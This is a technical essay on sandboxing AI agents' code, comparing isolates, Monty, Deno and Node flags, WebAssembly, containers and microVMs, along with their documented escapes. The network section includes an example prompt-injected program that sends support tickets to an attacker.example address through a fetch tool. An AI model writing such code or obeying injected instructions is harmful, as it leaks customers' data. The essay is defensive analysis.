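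Cloudflare's case for isolates relies heavily on their speed. Varda and colleagues say that an isolate starts in a few milliseconds and uses a few megabytes of memory, making it around 100 times faster than a typical container and 10 to 100 times more memory-efficient. These are round figures from the company that sells the service, and the comparison may already be out of date. On 30 September 2026, Cloudflare (2026) announced that its own containers now start six times faster. If the earlier comparison had been with those containers, the factor of 100 would have fallen to about 17.

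Speed matters for security as well as cost. Varda and colleagues note that slow containers tempt developers to reuse one for several tasks, which could let one task read data left by another. Isolates are lightweight enough that the host can run each program in a new one and then discard it. But the host depends on V8 to keep the programs apart, and Varda and colleagues concede that security bugs are more common in V8 than in the software that separates virtual machines.

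### Pausing a program for approval

By June 2026, Code Mode also had a runtime that keeps records outside the isolate. It intercepts each binding call before the host carries it out, numbers it in sequence, and logs its arguments and, in most cases, its result. Developers can require a person to approve certain calls. Approval may take hours, and the isolate doesn't last that long, so Cloudflare reruns the program from the beginning.

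Suppose the company requires approval for refunds, and the model has written the earlier loop that gives 10 dollars to everyone with a late delivery:

1. The program lists the tickets, looks up the first customer and calls `refunds.issue`. The runtime records the refund as pending and stops the program.
2. An employee sees the name of the function and its arguments, and approves the refund.
3. The host runs the same code in a new isolate. When the program asks for the tickets and the customer, the runtime returns the results it recorded the first time.
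4. The program reaches the refund again. The host now issues it, and the program continues until the second refund, where it stops again.

Thirty refunds would take thirty approvals and thirty-one runs. If a later run makes a different call from the one in the log, perhaps because the code depends on the time of day, the runtime stops the run with an error, so an employee's approval of one refund can't carry over to a different one.

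This restores the pause between calls that programs otherwise lose, but its value depends on the employee's judgement. The record of a pending call shows the order number and the 10 dollars but not the filter that selected the order, so the company's own software would have to display the code as well. An employee who has approved twenty nearly identical refunds may not look closely at the next ten. The recorded results can also go out of date. If a colleague refunds a customer by hand while the program is waiting, the program still works from the old list of tickets and may request a second refund.

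The runtime can also roll back a run by calling an undo function for each completed call, in reverse order. This works only for bindings whose developers wrote such a function.

If developers use Code Mode without this runtime, Cloudflare leaves any tool marked as needing approval out of the program's bindings. The program could still prepare a list of customers to refund, but the model would have to request each refund as a separate tool call, as OpenAI also recommends.

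## How do restricted interpreters and permission flags withhold authority?

Python has built-in functions for files and the network, as do Deno and Node.js, which run JavaScript outside the browser. The bare JavaScript in an isolate has none. A developer running agent code in these environments can either write a new interpreter without the dangerous functions or keep the existing interpreter and add checks that run before those functions do.

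Pydantic, which makes tools for Python developers, wrote a new interpreter called Monty. The company calls the more common approach, starting with a full system and locking it down, "working backwards", partly because every operating system has its own isolation tools to configure.

### Monty

Pydantic built Monty, an interpreter for a subset of Python, in the programming language Rust. Monty contains none of CPython, the standard Python interpreter, which can open files, start other processes and load libraries written in other languages. It translates the model's code into bytecode, a list of simple instructions, and executes them itself.

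None of those instructions can access the host. Pydantic's *Security Model* explains that a program without bindings can't read a file, open a network connection or start another process, because the interpreter has no code for doing so. It also can't read the host's environment variables, the settings that a process inherits when it starts, which often include passwords. By default, a program can still read the clock and get random numbers. The host can freeze the clock and fix the starting point of the random numbers, for much the same reasons that Hardened JavaScript disables both.

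The simplest way to grant anything more is to supply a function:

```python
from pydantic_monty import Monty

code = "issue_refund('A-1042', 20)"

with Monty() as pool:
    with pool.checkout() as session:
        session.feed_run(code, external_lookup={'issue_refund': issue_refund})
```

`checkout` reserves a worker, a separate process that runs the interpreter, and `feed_run` sends it the model's code. When the program uses a name that it hasn't defined, Monty looks for it in `external_lookup`, the table of outside names from Miller's loader. `issue_refund` is in the table, so the host runs it and returns the result. A call to `send_mail` would fail because it isn't in the table.

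The host can also give the program a Python object with a list of what the program may use. In Pydantic's example, the program can see the owner and balance of an account and call `withdraw`, but not `close`. These lists are empty by default. If a permitted method returns another object, the call fails unless the host has specified how to wrap that object. This guards against the problem with revoked ticket lists, where a seemingly harmless result carried a working `reply` function.

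Monty handles files in a similar way. When a program calls `open`, the interpreter pauses and passes a description of the operation to the host, which carries it out only within directories that the developer has attached. In CPython, by contrast, `open` accesses the file system directly.

Monty can't make a badly designed binding safe. Host functions run with the host's full authority, and Pydantic warns developers to treat the arguments to these functions as untrusted input. If a function accepts any file path and returns the contents, the program can read every file the host can, even though the interpreter has no access to files. Such a function makes the host a confused deputy, as does a `mail.send` that accepts any address.

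### Saving a paused program

Monty pauses at every host call, so the host can save the program there and continue it later. Pydantic's *Snapshots* explains that this is possible because the program has no open files, network connections or threads for the host to restore. Everything the program needs is in the interpreter's memory.

Suppose the support company wants an employee to approve each refund. Using the functions that Pydantic (2026) documents for version 1.7.0, the host could write:

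```python
code = """
for order in late_orders:
    issue_refund(order, 10)
"""

with Monty() as pool:
    with pool.checkout() as session:
        paused = session.feed_start(code, inputs={'late_orders': late_orders})
        print(paused.function_name, paused.args)  # issue_refund ('A-1042', 10)
        saved = paused.dump()

    # hours later, after an employee has approved the refund
    with pool.checkout() as session:
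        paused = session.load_snapshot(saved)
        receipt = issue_refund(*paused.args)
        paused = paused.resume({'return_value': receipt})
```

1. `feed_start` runs the program until it calls `issue_refund`. The host receives the function's name and arguments, but no money has moved.
2. `dump` converts the interpreter's state into bytes, including the program's variables and its place in the loop. The host can store the bytes in a database and use the worker for something else.
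3. Once an employee approves the refund, `load_snapshot` restores the program in a fresh session, which can be on another machine.
4. The host issues the refund, and `resume` gives the program the receipt as if the function had just returned it. The program continues to the second order and pauses again.

Unlike Cloudflare's approval runtime, Monty doesn't have to rerun the program after each approval, so thirty refunds need thirty approvals but only one run. The data can still go stale, because `late_orders` stays as it was when the program started.

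Pydantic says a snapshot takes a few kilobytes, compared with gigabytes for a small virtual machine. The snapshot is larger if the program has read a lot of data, and anyone who can read it may be able to recover that data.

Monty also doesn't check who produced the bytes, so an attacker who could edit a stored snapshot might change an order number after the employee had approved it. Pydantic tells developers to keep snapshots in trusted storage or to verify a cryptographic signature before loading them. Ideally, the host would also keep its own record of the approved call and compare it with the call in the snapshot before paying.

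### How mature is Monty?

Pydantic labelled Monty "experimental" from the start, and in April 2026 it launched a public contest that it hoped would justify dropping the label. It offered $5,000 for extracting a secret from a server that ran anyone's Python code with no protection other than Monty.

The sandbox lasted less than 48 hours. According to *Hack Monty* (Hewitt, 2026), the winner, Owen Kwan of Veria Labs, combined two bugs. Rust normally stops a program from using memory it has already released, but programmers can turn off some of these checks in code marked `unsafe`. Monty had such code, and an error in its memory clean-up released a list that was still in use. This let Kwan run code outside the interpreter and read the secret from an environment variable.

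Kwan's program had no binding for environment variables, so under Miller's rules it couldn't read them. Those rules hold only if the interpreter enforces them correctly, and a reviewer who checks every binding can still miss a fault in the interpreter's thousands of lines of code.

Pydantic fixed the flaw in version 0.0.16. Hewitt finds it encouraging that more than a million attacks on the server produced only this one escape. The attacks came from about 650 internet addresses and led to 65 submissions, but the speed of the escape seems more informative than the number of attacks. A second researcher, Stanislav Fort, found a weakness in the contest's virtual filesystem, though it didn't reveal the secret. Hewitt reports that Pydantic has re-audited the `unsafe` code and expects no more memory-safety faults, but concedes that the design of the clean-up still doesn't rule out the kind of omission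 that allowed the escape.

Pydantic still labelled Monty experimental after the contest. Its page for a later release, *monty 0.0.21*, warned that the project was "not ready for prime time". Version 1.7.0, released on 24 November 2026, no longer has this warning and is labelled "Production/Stable", a status that publishers choose for their own packages.

Independent evidence is thinner. In May 2026, Willison had an AI coding agent examine Monty. *pydantic-monty investigation* (Willison, 2026) reports that unsupported features generally produced clean errors and that the resource limits appeared to work, but this is a much weaker test than a determined attacker would provide. Pydantic's *Hack Monty* invited people to a third contest in August, again with no second sandbox around the interpreter.

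Even Monty's stable release comes with a warning that hostile input can crash the process. Pydantic's Python and JavaScript packages therefore run the interpreter in workers and replace any that crash. On an ordinary server, a worker starts with an almost empty environment, so the host's passwords aren't in its memory. But a worker is not an operating-system sandbox, so an attacker who took one over would probably have the file and network access of the account it runs under. By default, each worker can serve up to 1,000 sessions, and Pydantic advises lowering this limit to one when users don't trust each other.

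The workers make Monty slower to start. An early version ran inside the host's own process and started in about 0.004 milliseconds. According to Pydantic's *Monty*, a new sandbox now takes 0.8 milliseconds to start, compared with 195 for a local Docker container. That comparison favours Monty because its workers are already running when timing begins, while the container still has to start.

### Deno's permission flags

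Deno combines the V8 engine with functions for files, networks and processes. Every program can name these functions, but Deno checks the program's permissions before carrying them out. Deno's *Permissions* explains that a program starts without access to any of them. The person who starts it grants access with flags on the command line:

- `--allow-read` and `--allow-write` give access to files.
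- `--allow-net` lets the program use the network.
- `--allow-env` lets it read environment variables.
- `--allow-sys` reveals information about the machine.
- `--allow-import` lets it load code from other websites.
- `--allow-run` lets it start other programs.
- `--allow-ffi` lets it load native libraries, which are compiled code that runs outside the JavaScript engine.

Developers can narrow nearly all of these flags to particular paths, servers or variables, according to OpenReplay's *Deno Permissions Model Explained*. Deno also has matching `--deny` flags, which take precedence. If a program needs a permission it lacks, Deno can ask the user at the terminal. An unattended agent should run with `--no-prompt`, so that the request fails instead of waiting for someone to approve it.

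The support company might start its agent's program like this:

```
deno run --no-prompt --allow-net=api.payments.example \
  --allow-env=PAYMENT_KEY agent.js
```

The program can now contact only one server and read only one variable, a large improvement on full access. But the flag specifies the server without limiting the actions the program can take, so the program can still use the key to issue a $5,000 refund or print the key for the model to read.

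A host can avoid this by using the flags only to block outside access. It starts Deno with no permissions and exchanges messages with the program through standard input and output, the text channels that every process has. The host can then offer a 50-dollar refund function over those channels without giving the program the key.

Flags also apply to the process as a whole. If `agent.js` imports a library that formats dates, the library can contact the payment server and read the key too. A developer can't use these flags to give network access to the refund function but not to the date library. So Deno greatly reduces ambient authority but doesn't eliminate it.

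Some permissions can let a program escape all its other restrictions. A program started through `--allow-run` runs as a separate operating-system process, and Deno's restrictions don't apply to it. In Deno's example, a script allowed to start only `deno` can launch a new copy with `--allow-all` and escape every limit. Deno recommends allowing only specific, trusted programs, such as `git`, but even `git` needs care because it can be configured to run other commands.

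Native libraries are also dangerous because Deno enforces its permissions in the JavaScript layer, which a native library can bypass by calling the operating system directly.

File access that is too broad can have the same effect. Vulners' *CVE 2024 34346*, an entry in a database of security flaws, describes a problem with the special files that some operating systems use to expose a running process. A program with permission to read every file could use them to read environment variables, and one with permission to write every file could gain full access by altering Deno's own memory. Deno's documentation hadn't warned users that file permissions could give a program this additional access, and the flags themselves didn't show it.

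Deno offers protection beyond permission flags for code written by AI. Deno's *Security* describes Deno Sandbox, a separate service that runs "untrusted or AI-generated workloads" in short-lived virtual machines. The service keeps secrets out of the machine and inserts them only into requests to approved servers, much like the gateways that Cloudflare supports.

### Node's permission model

Unlike Deno, Node.js gives programs the full access of the user's account by default. Starting Node with the `--permission` flag blocks access to files, other processes and native add-ons, and further flags restore each kind of access. As in Deno, permissions apply to the whole process, not to individual functions or modules.

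The two projects differ most in what they promise. Node's permission model, which its documentation compares to a seat belt, keeps trusted code from changing a file or using a resource by accident. It offers no security guarantee against malicious code, which can bypass the restrictions. A model that has read a stranger's support ticket may write malicious code, so Node's flags can't be the main barrier around an agent's program. They could still limit the damage from a bug, such as one that makes a script delete the wrong directory.

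### Filtering names in ordinary Python

Many developers want agents to use ordinary Python with all its libraries. One way to restrict that code is to run it in CPython but remove `open`, block most imports and reject any program that contains a forbidden name. The image-handling benchmark described earlier includes checks of this kind, which may be adequate when nobody is trying to break out.

The approach has a poor record because Python objects are closely linked. Even an empty list links to its class, which links to the base class of all others, and from there a program can reach classes that the host has loaded. Functions link to the variables of the module that defined them. A program can often follow such links to a powerful function without writing its name. The `constructor` trick in JavaScript exploits the same weakness. Unlike Hardened JavaScript, a filter leaves the shared objects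 unchanged and tries to recognise every route through them.

Python once included a module for restricted execution, `rexec`. Python's developers disabled it in version 2.3, in 2003, because a new kind of class had opened new ways to escape the restrictions and nobody had the time or interest to close them.

Later projects have had similar problems. RestrictedPython is a long-maintained package that limits what Python code can do. Advisories in 2023 described one escape through the records Python keeps of running functions and one leak through Python's text-formatting features. A 2025 advisory for smolagents, Hugging Face's agent library, reported that code could escape the library's local Python executor through modules and functions that the executor allowed. In each case, the developers had overlooked a way around the restrictions through something that seemed harmless.

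Hermetic blocks file and network operations inside a Python process. Its *Threat Model* recommends using it alone only to prevent accidental side effects. For code that may be hostile, the document recommends running Hermetic inside an operating-system sandbox, which it calls "the actual security boundary".

### WebAssembly

WebAssembly is an instruction format that many languages can compile to, including C and Rust. A WebAssembly module has its own memory and, like Monty's bytecode, no instruction for opening a file or contacting a server. It can call only its own functions and its imports, which are the functions the host supplies when it loads the module. A module with no imports can compute but can't open files or contact servers.

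Imports therefore play the same role as bindings, but they are more primitive. In basic WebAssembly, a module passes numbers to an import, not text or objects. To request a refund for order A-1042, the module writes the order number into its own memory and passes the position and length of the text. The host then has to read the text from that memory and check it, so each import usually needs extra code between the module and the real function.

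WebAssembly also offers a way to run ordinary Python without filtering names. In Pyodide, a version of CPython compiled to WebAssembly, a program that finds a hidden `open` function gains little, because that function can reach only what the surrounding host provides. But Pyodide normally lets Python code use the JavaScript functions around it, including those for network requests, so an agent's program could use them unless the host removes them.

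A standard set of imports called WASI covers common needs such as files, clocks and environment variables. *MCP-SandboxScan* (Tan, Hao and colleagues, 2026) uses WASI to examine MCP tools from outside developers before anyone installs them. The system gives each tool access to one directory and a few chosen environment variables, and by default it blocks or controls network access. These restrictions work only for tools that can run as WebAssembly. The system runs the others as normal programs, and the paper recommends an operating-system sandbox for those.

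Developers can also run a restricted interpreter inside WebAssembly. Willison did this with Monty in February 2026 and called the result a "sandbox-in-a-sandbox" (*Running Pydantic’s Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*, 2026). If Kwan had attacked such a version, the same bug would probably have left him inside the WebAssembly module, with access only to its imports.

### Defaults, grants and mistakes

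| Approach | What a program can do by default | What the host grants | What one mistake can expose |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monty | Compute, read the clock and get random numbers | A function, chosen parts of an object, or a directory | Everything a careless host function can reach, or the worker's operating-system access if the interpreter has a memory bug |
| Deno flags | Compute, with no access to files, network or other programs | A path, server, variable or program, for the whole process | Everything the user's account can reach, if the program can start a shell or load native code |
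| Node flags | Use the full access of the user's account, until someone adds `--permission` | A path or a type of action, for the whole process | Everything the user's account can reach, if malicious code bypasses the checks |
| Filtered Python | Anything the filter fails to block | The names and modules that the filter lets through | Everything the host process can reach, including passwords in its memory |
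| WebAssembly | Compute in its own memory | An imported function | Everything a careless import can reach, or the host process if the WebAssembly engine has a bug |

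## How strong is an isolate compared with a container or a virtual machine?

Kwan's attack on Monty was an escape, because his program got past the interpreter and read a secret that no binding offered. Stronger isolation makes escapes harder, but it does not make it harder for a program to misuse the bindings it has. For example, a support program can refund the wrong thirty customers without leaving its sandbox.

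A program that escaped into the host's memory could still take the payment key and bypass the schema's 50-dollar limit, so the limit is only as reliable as the isolation between the program and the host.

### What an attacker would have to defeat

A tenant is a customer whose code runs on a shared machine. With isolates, many tenants share one operating-system process and one range of memory addresses, so V8 has to keep each program inside its own heap. Schwarzl and Pedersen write in *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers* that tens of thousands of tenants can share a process. An attacker who found a V8 bug that let a program read any address could read all their data, unless something else stopped the program.

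An agent program can run in the same process as its host. Varda and colleagues explain that a one-off Dynamic Worker usually runs on the same thread as the Worker that created it. In that case, the support agent's program would share a process with the code that holds the payment key.

Containers run in separate processes, so the processor keeps their memory apart. The Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, also gives each container its own files and network settings. But all containers on a machine send their requests, such as opening a file or sending data, to that same kernel. Linux has several hundred kinds of request, known as system calls, and a bug in the code that handles any of them might let a container take over the machine. An attacker could also target the container runtime, which sets up containers and needs broad privileges on the host to do so.

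Google's gVisor adds a second kernel between the container and the host's kernel, and runs it as an ordinary program in user space. This second kernel answers most system calls itself and makes only a limited set of calls to the host. An attacker generally has to take over gVisor and then find a bug in the host's kernel that those few calls can reach. But gVisor makes system calls slower, and some programs fail because it doesn't support everything that Linux does.

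A virtual machine has its own kernel. A hypervisor, the software that divides a physical machine into virtual ones, uses processor features to keep them apart. An attacker who controls everything inside the virtual machine still has to defeat the hypervisor or the device model, the program that imitates disks, network cards and other hardware. QEMU, a widely used device model, imitates a lot of hardware, some of it obsolete, and an attacker could target any of that code.

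Cloud companies traditionally had to choose between virtual machines, which had strong security but high overhead, and containers, which had weaker security but little overhead (Brooker, 2020). Amazon Web Services (AWS) tried to avoid this choice with Firecracker, a small replacement for QEMU, written in Rust, that works with KVM, the hypervisor in the Linux kernel (Agache, Brooker and colleagues, 2020). Engineers call the resulting machines microVMs.

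### Start-up time and memory

Most published figures come from companies that sell one of these designs. Lin (2026) summarises the AWS paper's Firecracker results in *Paper Notes*, and Browserbase's *What is Firecracker* gives similar numbers with more detail on what they cover.

| Design | Start-up time | Memory | Who gives the figures |
|---|---|---|---|
| Isolate | A few milliseconds | A few megabytes | Varda and colleagues, for their own service |
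| Container | Hundreds of milliseconds | Hundreds of megabytes | Varda and colleagues, for typical containers |
| Firecracker microVM | About 125 milliseconds | About 3 megabytes of overhead | Lin, from the AWS paper |

The table's memory figures for microVMs and containers measure different things, so they don't show that a microVM needs less memory. Browserbase explains that Firecracker's figure covers only the memory the host uses to manage each machine. The guest's kernel and the agent's program need additional memory. Similarly, the 125-millisecond startup time covers only the period until the guest starts its first process, before it loads Python or any of the agent's code. Pydantic measured 195 milliseconds for a local Docker container, which suggests that microVMs and containers start at roughly the same speed.

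Isolates are clearly faster than containers and virtual machines. The difference hardly matters for a single run, since a language model usually takes seconds to write the program. It matters much more to a company that runs thousands of agent programs at once and pays for the memory each one uses.

### How often does each wall fail?

Cloudflare concedes in its *Security model* that V8 has more security bugs than typical hypervisors, because V8 is extraordinarily complicated and so offers more places to attack. The company adds that few programs get as much scrutiny. Google pays five-figure rewards for escapes from V8 and runs systems that search for bugs automatically.

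The record for 2026 supports the concession. By 10 November, Google had patched eight Chrome flaws that attackers were already exploiting, according to *Chrome Update Patches Exploited XML Zero-Day, Eighth This Year* (Kovacs, 2026). At least three were in V8, including one from June listed in IBTimes Australia's *Google Patches Eighth Actively Exploited Chrome Zero-Day of 2026* (2026) and two that Google fixed within a week in early September. The Hacker News' *New Chrome Zero-Day (CVE-2026-2441) Under Active Attack* (2026) also counts eight Chrome flaws for 2025, though some of those may only have been demonstrated, not used in attacks.

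The September flaws were both memory errors. In one, V8 treated an object as the wrong type, as Help Net Security's *Google patches actively exploited Chrome zero-day (CVE-2026-85046)* (2026) reports. In the other, it wrote outside the memory set aside for an object, according to Help Net Security's *Google fixes yet another actively exploited Chrome zero-day (CVE-2026-87491)* (2026). Google says an attacker could run code "inside the sandbox", the restricted process that Chrome puts around a web page. The attacker would have needed another flaw to reach the rest of the computer, but a server that relies on V8 alone has no such second barrier.

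Flaws in container runtimes are also fairly frequent. In November 2025, the developers of runc, the runtime that Docker and many other systems use, fixed three flaws that could let a container break out. CNCF's *runc container breakout vulnerabilities a technical overview* (2025) rates the severity of two of them at 7.3 out of 10. The flaws resemble the confused deputy at Tymshare, because runc used the host's authority on file paths that a malicious container could redirect. The developers' advisory, in the vulnerability database GCVE, recommends a setting that removes the special rights that the container's administrator account has on the host, which would have blocked the worst effects.

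A related flaw followed in June 2026, but Sarai (2026) gave it a severity score of only 3.3 in *CVE-2026-41579*. GitLab's *Advisories for Golang/Github.com/Opencontainers/Runc package* notes that attackers can't exploit it under Docker.

The shared kernel is probably the greater worry. Root.cz's *Chyba v nf_tables způsobená jedním vykřičníkem umožňuje získat roota* describes a flaw, fixed in February 2026, in which one misplaced exclamation mark in the kernel's network filter let an ordinary user become administrator and escape a container. Cybernews' *Onslaught of Linux kernel bugs forces cyber pros to rethink security boundaries* quotes the security company Depthfirst, which counted 5,976 kernel vulnerabilities published since the start of the year and concluded that containers are no longer a security boundary. But the kernel's developers list almost any bug that might affect security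 as a vulnerability, and most of those bugs probably can't get anyone out of a container.

Tianon Gravi, who has worked with containers for more than 13 years, disagrees with the conclusion too. In a post excerpted in Tux Machines' *Security Leftovers* (2026), he calls the claim that containers are no boundary "technically defensible but practically sloppy". He accepts that an attack using a kernel flaw can cross from one container to another where a virtual machine would have stopped it, and he lists three escapes since 2019 that affected correctly configured containers. He also says in his title that containers need "some assembly", and runc's optional account setting is a good example.

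Virtual machines have a better record, but they also had a bad year in 2026. SC Media's *Linux bug dormant for 16 years can cause a VM escape* reports on Januscape, a memory error in KVM dating from 2010. Most installations never run the faulty code, which is mainly needed for running one virtual machine inside another.

PwnEscape, from October, was more serious for agent sandboxes. Paulos Yibelo found it in a contest where the hosting company Vercel offered up to a million dollars for breaking out of its sandbox. The flaw was in the host kernel's network code, which handles packets from the virtual machine, and not in Firecracker or KVM. According to iTnews' *Researchers turn PwnEscape Linux flaw into Firecracker breakout*, Yibelo went on to take full control of a host from inside a Firecracker microVM. He had left out the jailer, an outer sandbox that production systems are meant to put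 around Firecracker, and AWS said its services weren't affected. But Gerke, in *Kritische Sicherheitslücke im Linux-Kernel*, reports that Yibelo could read small pieces of the host's memory on Vercel's live service.

OpenNET's *Уязвимость в Kata Containers, позволяющая обойти изоляцию контейнера* describes another 2026 escape, this one from Kata Containers, which runs each container in a virtual machine. The fault was in a helper on the host that shares files with the guest.

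In both PwnEscape and the Kata flaw, the hypervisor worked as intended, and the attack went through a service that the host ran for the guest. An agent program that acts only through bindings needs neither a network card nor a shared directory. Leaving both out of the virtual machine would probably have avoided both flaws, although the host still needs some channel for the binding calls. Restricting what a program can do therefore also reduces the number of host services an attacker can target.

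These counts reflect where people look more than how many bugs exist. Chrome has billions of users, which gives attackers a strong reason to search it for flaws. AI systems now find some of these flaws, so past rates may be a poor guide to future ones. Still, the usual ranking from hardest to easiest to escape seems right: microVM, gVisor, container, bare isolate.

### What Cloudflare adds to V8

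Cloudflare supplements its isolates with several defences that use less processor time than running each tenant in a separate process. Separate processes would be the most direct remedy for V8's flaws, but many Workers run for less than a millisecond at a time, and switching between processes that often can easily increase processor use tenfold.

Fast patching is one way to protect isolates. V8 is open source, so attackers can locate a flaw by reading its published fix. Cloudflare's systems build a new version as soon as a fix appears, and it usually reaches production in under 24 hours. The company compares this with Chrome, where Google had cut the same delay from 33 days to 15. Linux distributions can be slower. SUSE and Ubuntu were still preparing some of their fixes for PwnEscape at the end of October, about two weeks after it was disclosed. A well-run isolate service may therefore spend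 less time exposed to a known flaw than a neglected virtual machine host.

Patching can't help before a fix exists. Researchers reported the two September flaws in V8 to Google in the first week of August, and Chrome's updates came out about a month later.

Cloudflare also puts the whole process in an outer sandbox, using the same kernel features that containers use. A container engine has to leave some files accessible because it starts the tenant's program from disk. Cloudflare applies its restrictions after its own software has started but before it loads any tenant's code, so it can give the process an empty filesystem and block every system call that deals with files. The process has no network access and can only exchange messages with a few other processes on the same machine. One of these, the supervisor, supplies tenants' code only if the request includes the encryption key for that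 code, so an attacker who took over the process couldn't ask for a list of other tenants' programs.

This outer sandbox protects the machine more than it protects the tenants from each other, because an attacker who has taken over the process already shares memory with the other tenants in it. Cloudflare limits that damage by sorting tenants by how much it trusts them, so a free-plan customer, for example, never shares a process with a large enterprise. An agent's program and its host presumably belong to the same customer, so this sorting wouldn't separate them.

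### Memory keys and the V8 sandbox

Memory protection keys work inside a process. They are a feature of recent processors that labels areas of memory, so that a thread can use an area only while it holds the matching key. Corry and Gupta, in *Safe in the sandbox*, explain how Cloudflare uses them to separate isolates. The processor offers up to 15 keys, and V8 needs a few for itself, which leaves about 12. If each isolate gets one of the 12 at random, the chance that an attacker's isolate and its target have different keys is:

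1 − 1/12 = 11/12 ≈ 92%

In 92 percent of cases, the processor blocks the attempt, and Cloudflare stops the program and investigates. In the other 8 percent, the two isolates happen to share a key, so this defence does nothing.

Cloudflare improved on the 92 percent by combining the keys with the V8 sandbox. A heap normally contains pointers, which are complete memory addresses, and an attacker who corrupts one can direct it anywhere in the process. The V8 sandbox replaces these pointers with 32-bit distances from a fixed starting point. A 32-bit distance can span only 4 GiB, so even a corrupted one stays within that range. Another 4 GiB hold the program's data buffers, making 8 GiB per sandbox.

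Lists of numbers remain a risk, because a corrupted position in a list can still point past the end of the sandbox. Each number takes up to 8 bytes, so the furthest reach is:

2³² × 8 bytes = 32 GiB

Cloudflare therefore assigns the keys in rotation, so that no two sandboxes within 32 GiB of each other share one. With 12 keys and sandboxes packed side by side, the next sandbox with the same key would begin 12 × 8 = 96 GiB away. The keys block every attempt to exploit this kind of error. Corry and Gupta note that this assumes the attacker can only corrupt data. An attacker who could run arbitrary machine code could turn the keys off.

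Varda and colleagues say that Dynamic Workers get all these layers automatically. Developers who run V8 isolates on their own servers don't get them, and should probably put the isolates inside a container or microVM.

### Spectre

All the flaws so far were software bugs. Spectre is a class of attacks on the processor, and it can work even if V8 has no bugs. To save time, a processor predicts which instructions come next and runs them early. If the prediction was wrong, it discards the results, but data it fetched along the way may remain in its cache, a small store of fast memory. A program can measure which data arrives quickly to work out what the processor accessed, and so infer a secret it isn't allowed to read.

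Processors have protections against this between processes, but isolates share one. Google gave up on defending against Spectre within a process and gave each website its own. Cloudflare tries to make the measurements impractical:

- The clock stands still while a Worker computes. `Date.now()` returns the time of the last input or output, so a program that checks it before and after a calculation gets the same answer twice.
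- Workers can't use several threads or share memory, either of which could serve as a makeshift clock.
- The runtime monitors the processor's performance counters and moves any program with suspicious readings into its own process. A false alarm costs only some speed.
- A daily restart changes where everything is in memory.

*Dynamic Process Isolation* (2021) proposed the monitoring as a defence against Spectre attacks. It demonstrated one on Workers that used a clock elsewhere on the network and leaked 120 bits an hour. Cloudflare states in its *Security model* that it has not been able to develop a remote timing attack that works in production.

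That claim is out of date. *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service* (Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) reports an attack that leaked data from one Worker to another on Cloudflare's production system at up to 12 bits a second, with 99.16 percent accuracy. This is 360 times the earlier rate of 120 bits an hour. Once an attacker has found a 256-bit key in memory, reading it takes about 21 seconds at the new rate, compared with more than two hours at the old one. The researchers, some of whom work for Cloudflare, attacked only Workers that they controlled and took these measurements at night on a lightly loaded machine. The attack slowed on busy machines but still worked.

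The monitoring missed the attack partly because the runtime isolated suspicious programs only after they had finished, and some Workers can run for hours. Cloudflare has since changed this and deployed the memory keys and the V8 sandbox, which together block the published attack. Schwarzl and Pedersen report no sign that anyone had used it against customers. They also write that these defences are incomplete and that other variants might still work. Virtual machines have no complete defence against Spectre either, though they isolate tenants more strongly.

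Such an attack seems harder to launch from a capability-scoped program. The program can't contact an outside clock when network access is off, and the host can stop it after a few seconds. Bindings that return precise times would weaken this advantage.

### The limits of a stronger wall

Suppose the support company moved its agent's program from an isolate to a Firecracker microVM and kept the same four bindings. The payment key would be much safer from a bug in V8, since the program would no longer share a process with the host. But a hidden instruction in a ticket could still make the program refund every open order.

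Developers often give a program more power when they move it to a microVM. VentureBeat contrasts Cloudflare's isolates with Docker Sandboxes, which use microVMs so that agents can install packages, run commands and change files. These abilities are a good reason to choose strong isolation, but they also give the agent more to misuse.

The choice also depends on who owns the machine. A hosting company mainly needs to protect its tenants from each other, and few options are better for that than a microVM around each one. The support company's greatest risk is what its own agent does with customers' money and data. A microVM that contained a shell, an open network connection and the payment key would protect the machine's other tenants from the agent, but it would leave the support company at more risk than an isolate with four narrow bindings would.

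## Can the program still reach the network?

If the support agent's program can connect to any server, it can leak customers' details without `mail.send` by sending every ticket to a stranger's server in a web request. It can also use any credential it finds. If a customer has pasted a password into a ticket, the program can log in to that customer's account, even though the host never offered a binding for it.

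Models sometimes pick up credentials this way. According to OpenAI, the UK's AI Security Institute found in a 2026 security test with open internet access that GPT-5.6 Sol had reused a GitHub token that another lab's agent had left in public.

A host can turn the network off, inspect every request, or approve servers by name. The loosest option is to leave the network open and only keep the host's own keys away from the program.

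### Turning the network off

According to Cloudflare's *Egress control*, the most secure design for a Dynamic Worker combines `globalOutbound: null` with specific bindings. The main risk is that a developer forgets the setting, because the program then inherits the host's network access.

Lists of approved servers can go wrong in a similar way if the software treats an empty list as a missing setting. A 2025 bug in Anthropic's sandbox software had this effect. Users who approved no servers, the strictest choice, got no network restrictions until Anthropic patched the bug.

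### A fetch function behind a closed network

Turning the network off doesn't help if a binding turns it back on, as the function for fetching any web address does in Varda and Pai's example. It comes from an MCP server that provides the documentation for one of Cloudflare's projects on GitHub. The server's other three tools only fetch or search the project's documentation and code, but this one accepts any address:

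```typescript
fetch_generic_url_content: (
  input: { url: string }
) => Promise<{ [key: string]: any }>;
```

This function does its work outside the isolate, where `globalOutbound: null` has no effect. Suppose the support company connects the same server so that its agent can look up technical answers. A hidden instruction in a ticket could then lead the model to write:

```javascript
const open = await codemode.tickets_list({});
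const data = encodeURIComponent(JSON.stringify(open));
await codemode.fetch_generic_url_content({
  url: "https://attacker.example/?d=" + data,
});
```

The address contains the tickets, so the stranger's server can log them whatever it sends back. If they don't fit into one address, the program can split them across several requests. The tool respects robots.txt, which lists the pages a site doesn't want automated visitors to fetch, but the stranger writes that file for his own server and can allow every page.

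The call satisfies the schema because every address is a string. A stricter schema would help only a little. JSON Schema, the usual format for tool schemas, can use a pattern to require that every address begin with `https://github.com/`. The program could still put data in the rest of the address, and the pattern doesn't restrict where the server might redirect the request.

The developers came closer to what they wanted in the tool's description, where they instruct the model to use the function for addresses mentioned in documentation it has already fetched. But the schema can't express that limit, because it describes the arguments of one call and the limit depends on the result of an earlier call.

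The host can enforce the limit by choosing the addresses itself. Before the program starts, the host fetches the documentation, collects the links to sites it trusts, and creates a binding that holds the list:

```javascript
// runs in the host
export class DocPages extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async read(n) {
    const { links } = this.ctx.props;
    if (!Number.isInteger(n) || n < 0 || n >= links.length) {
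      throw new Error("no such page");
    }
    const res = await fetch(links[n], { redirect: "manual" });
    if (!res.ok) throw new Error("page not available");
    return await res.text();
  }
}

const pages = ctx.exports.DocPages({ props: { links } });
```

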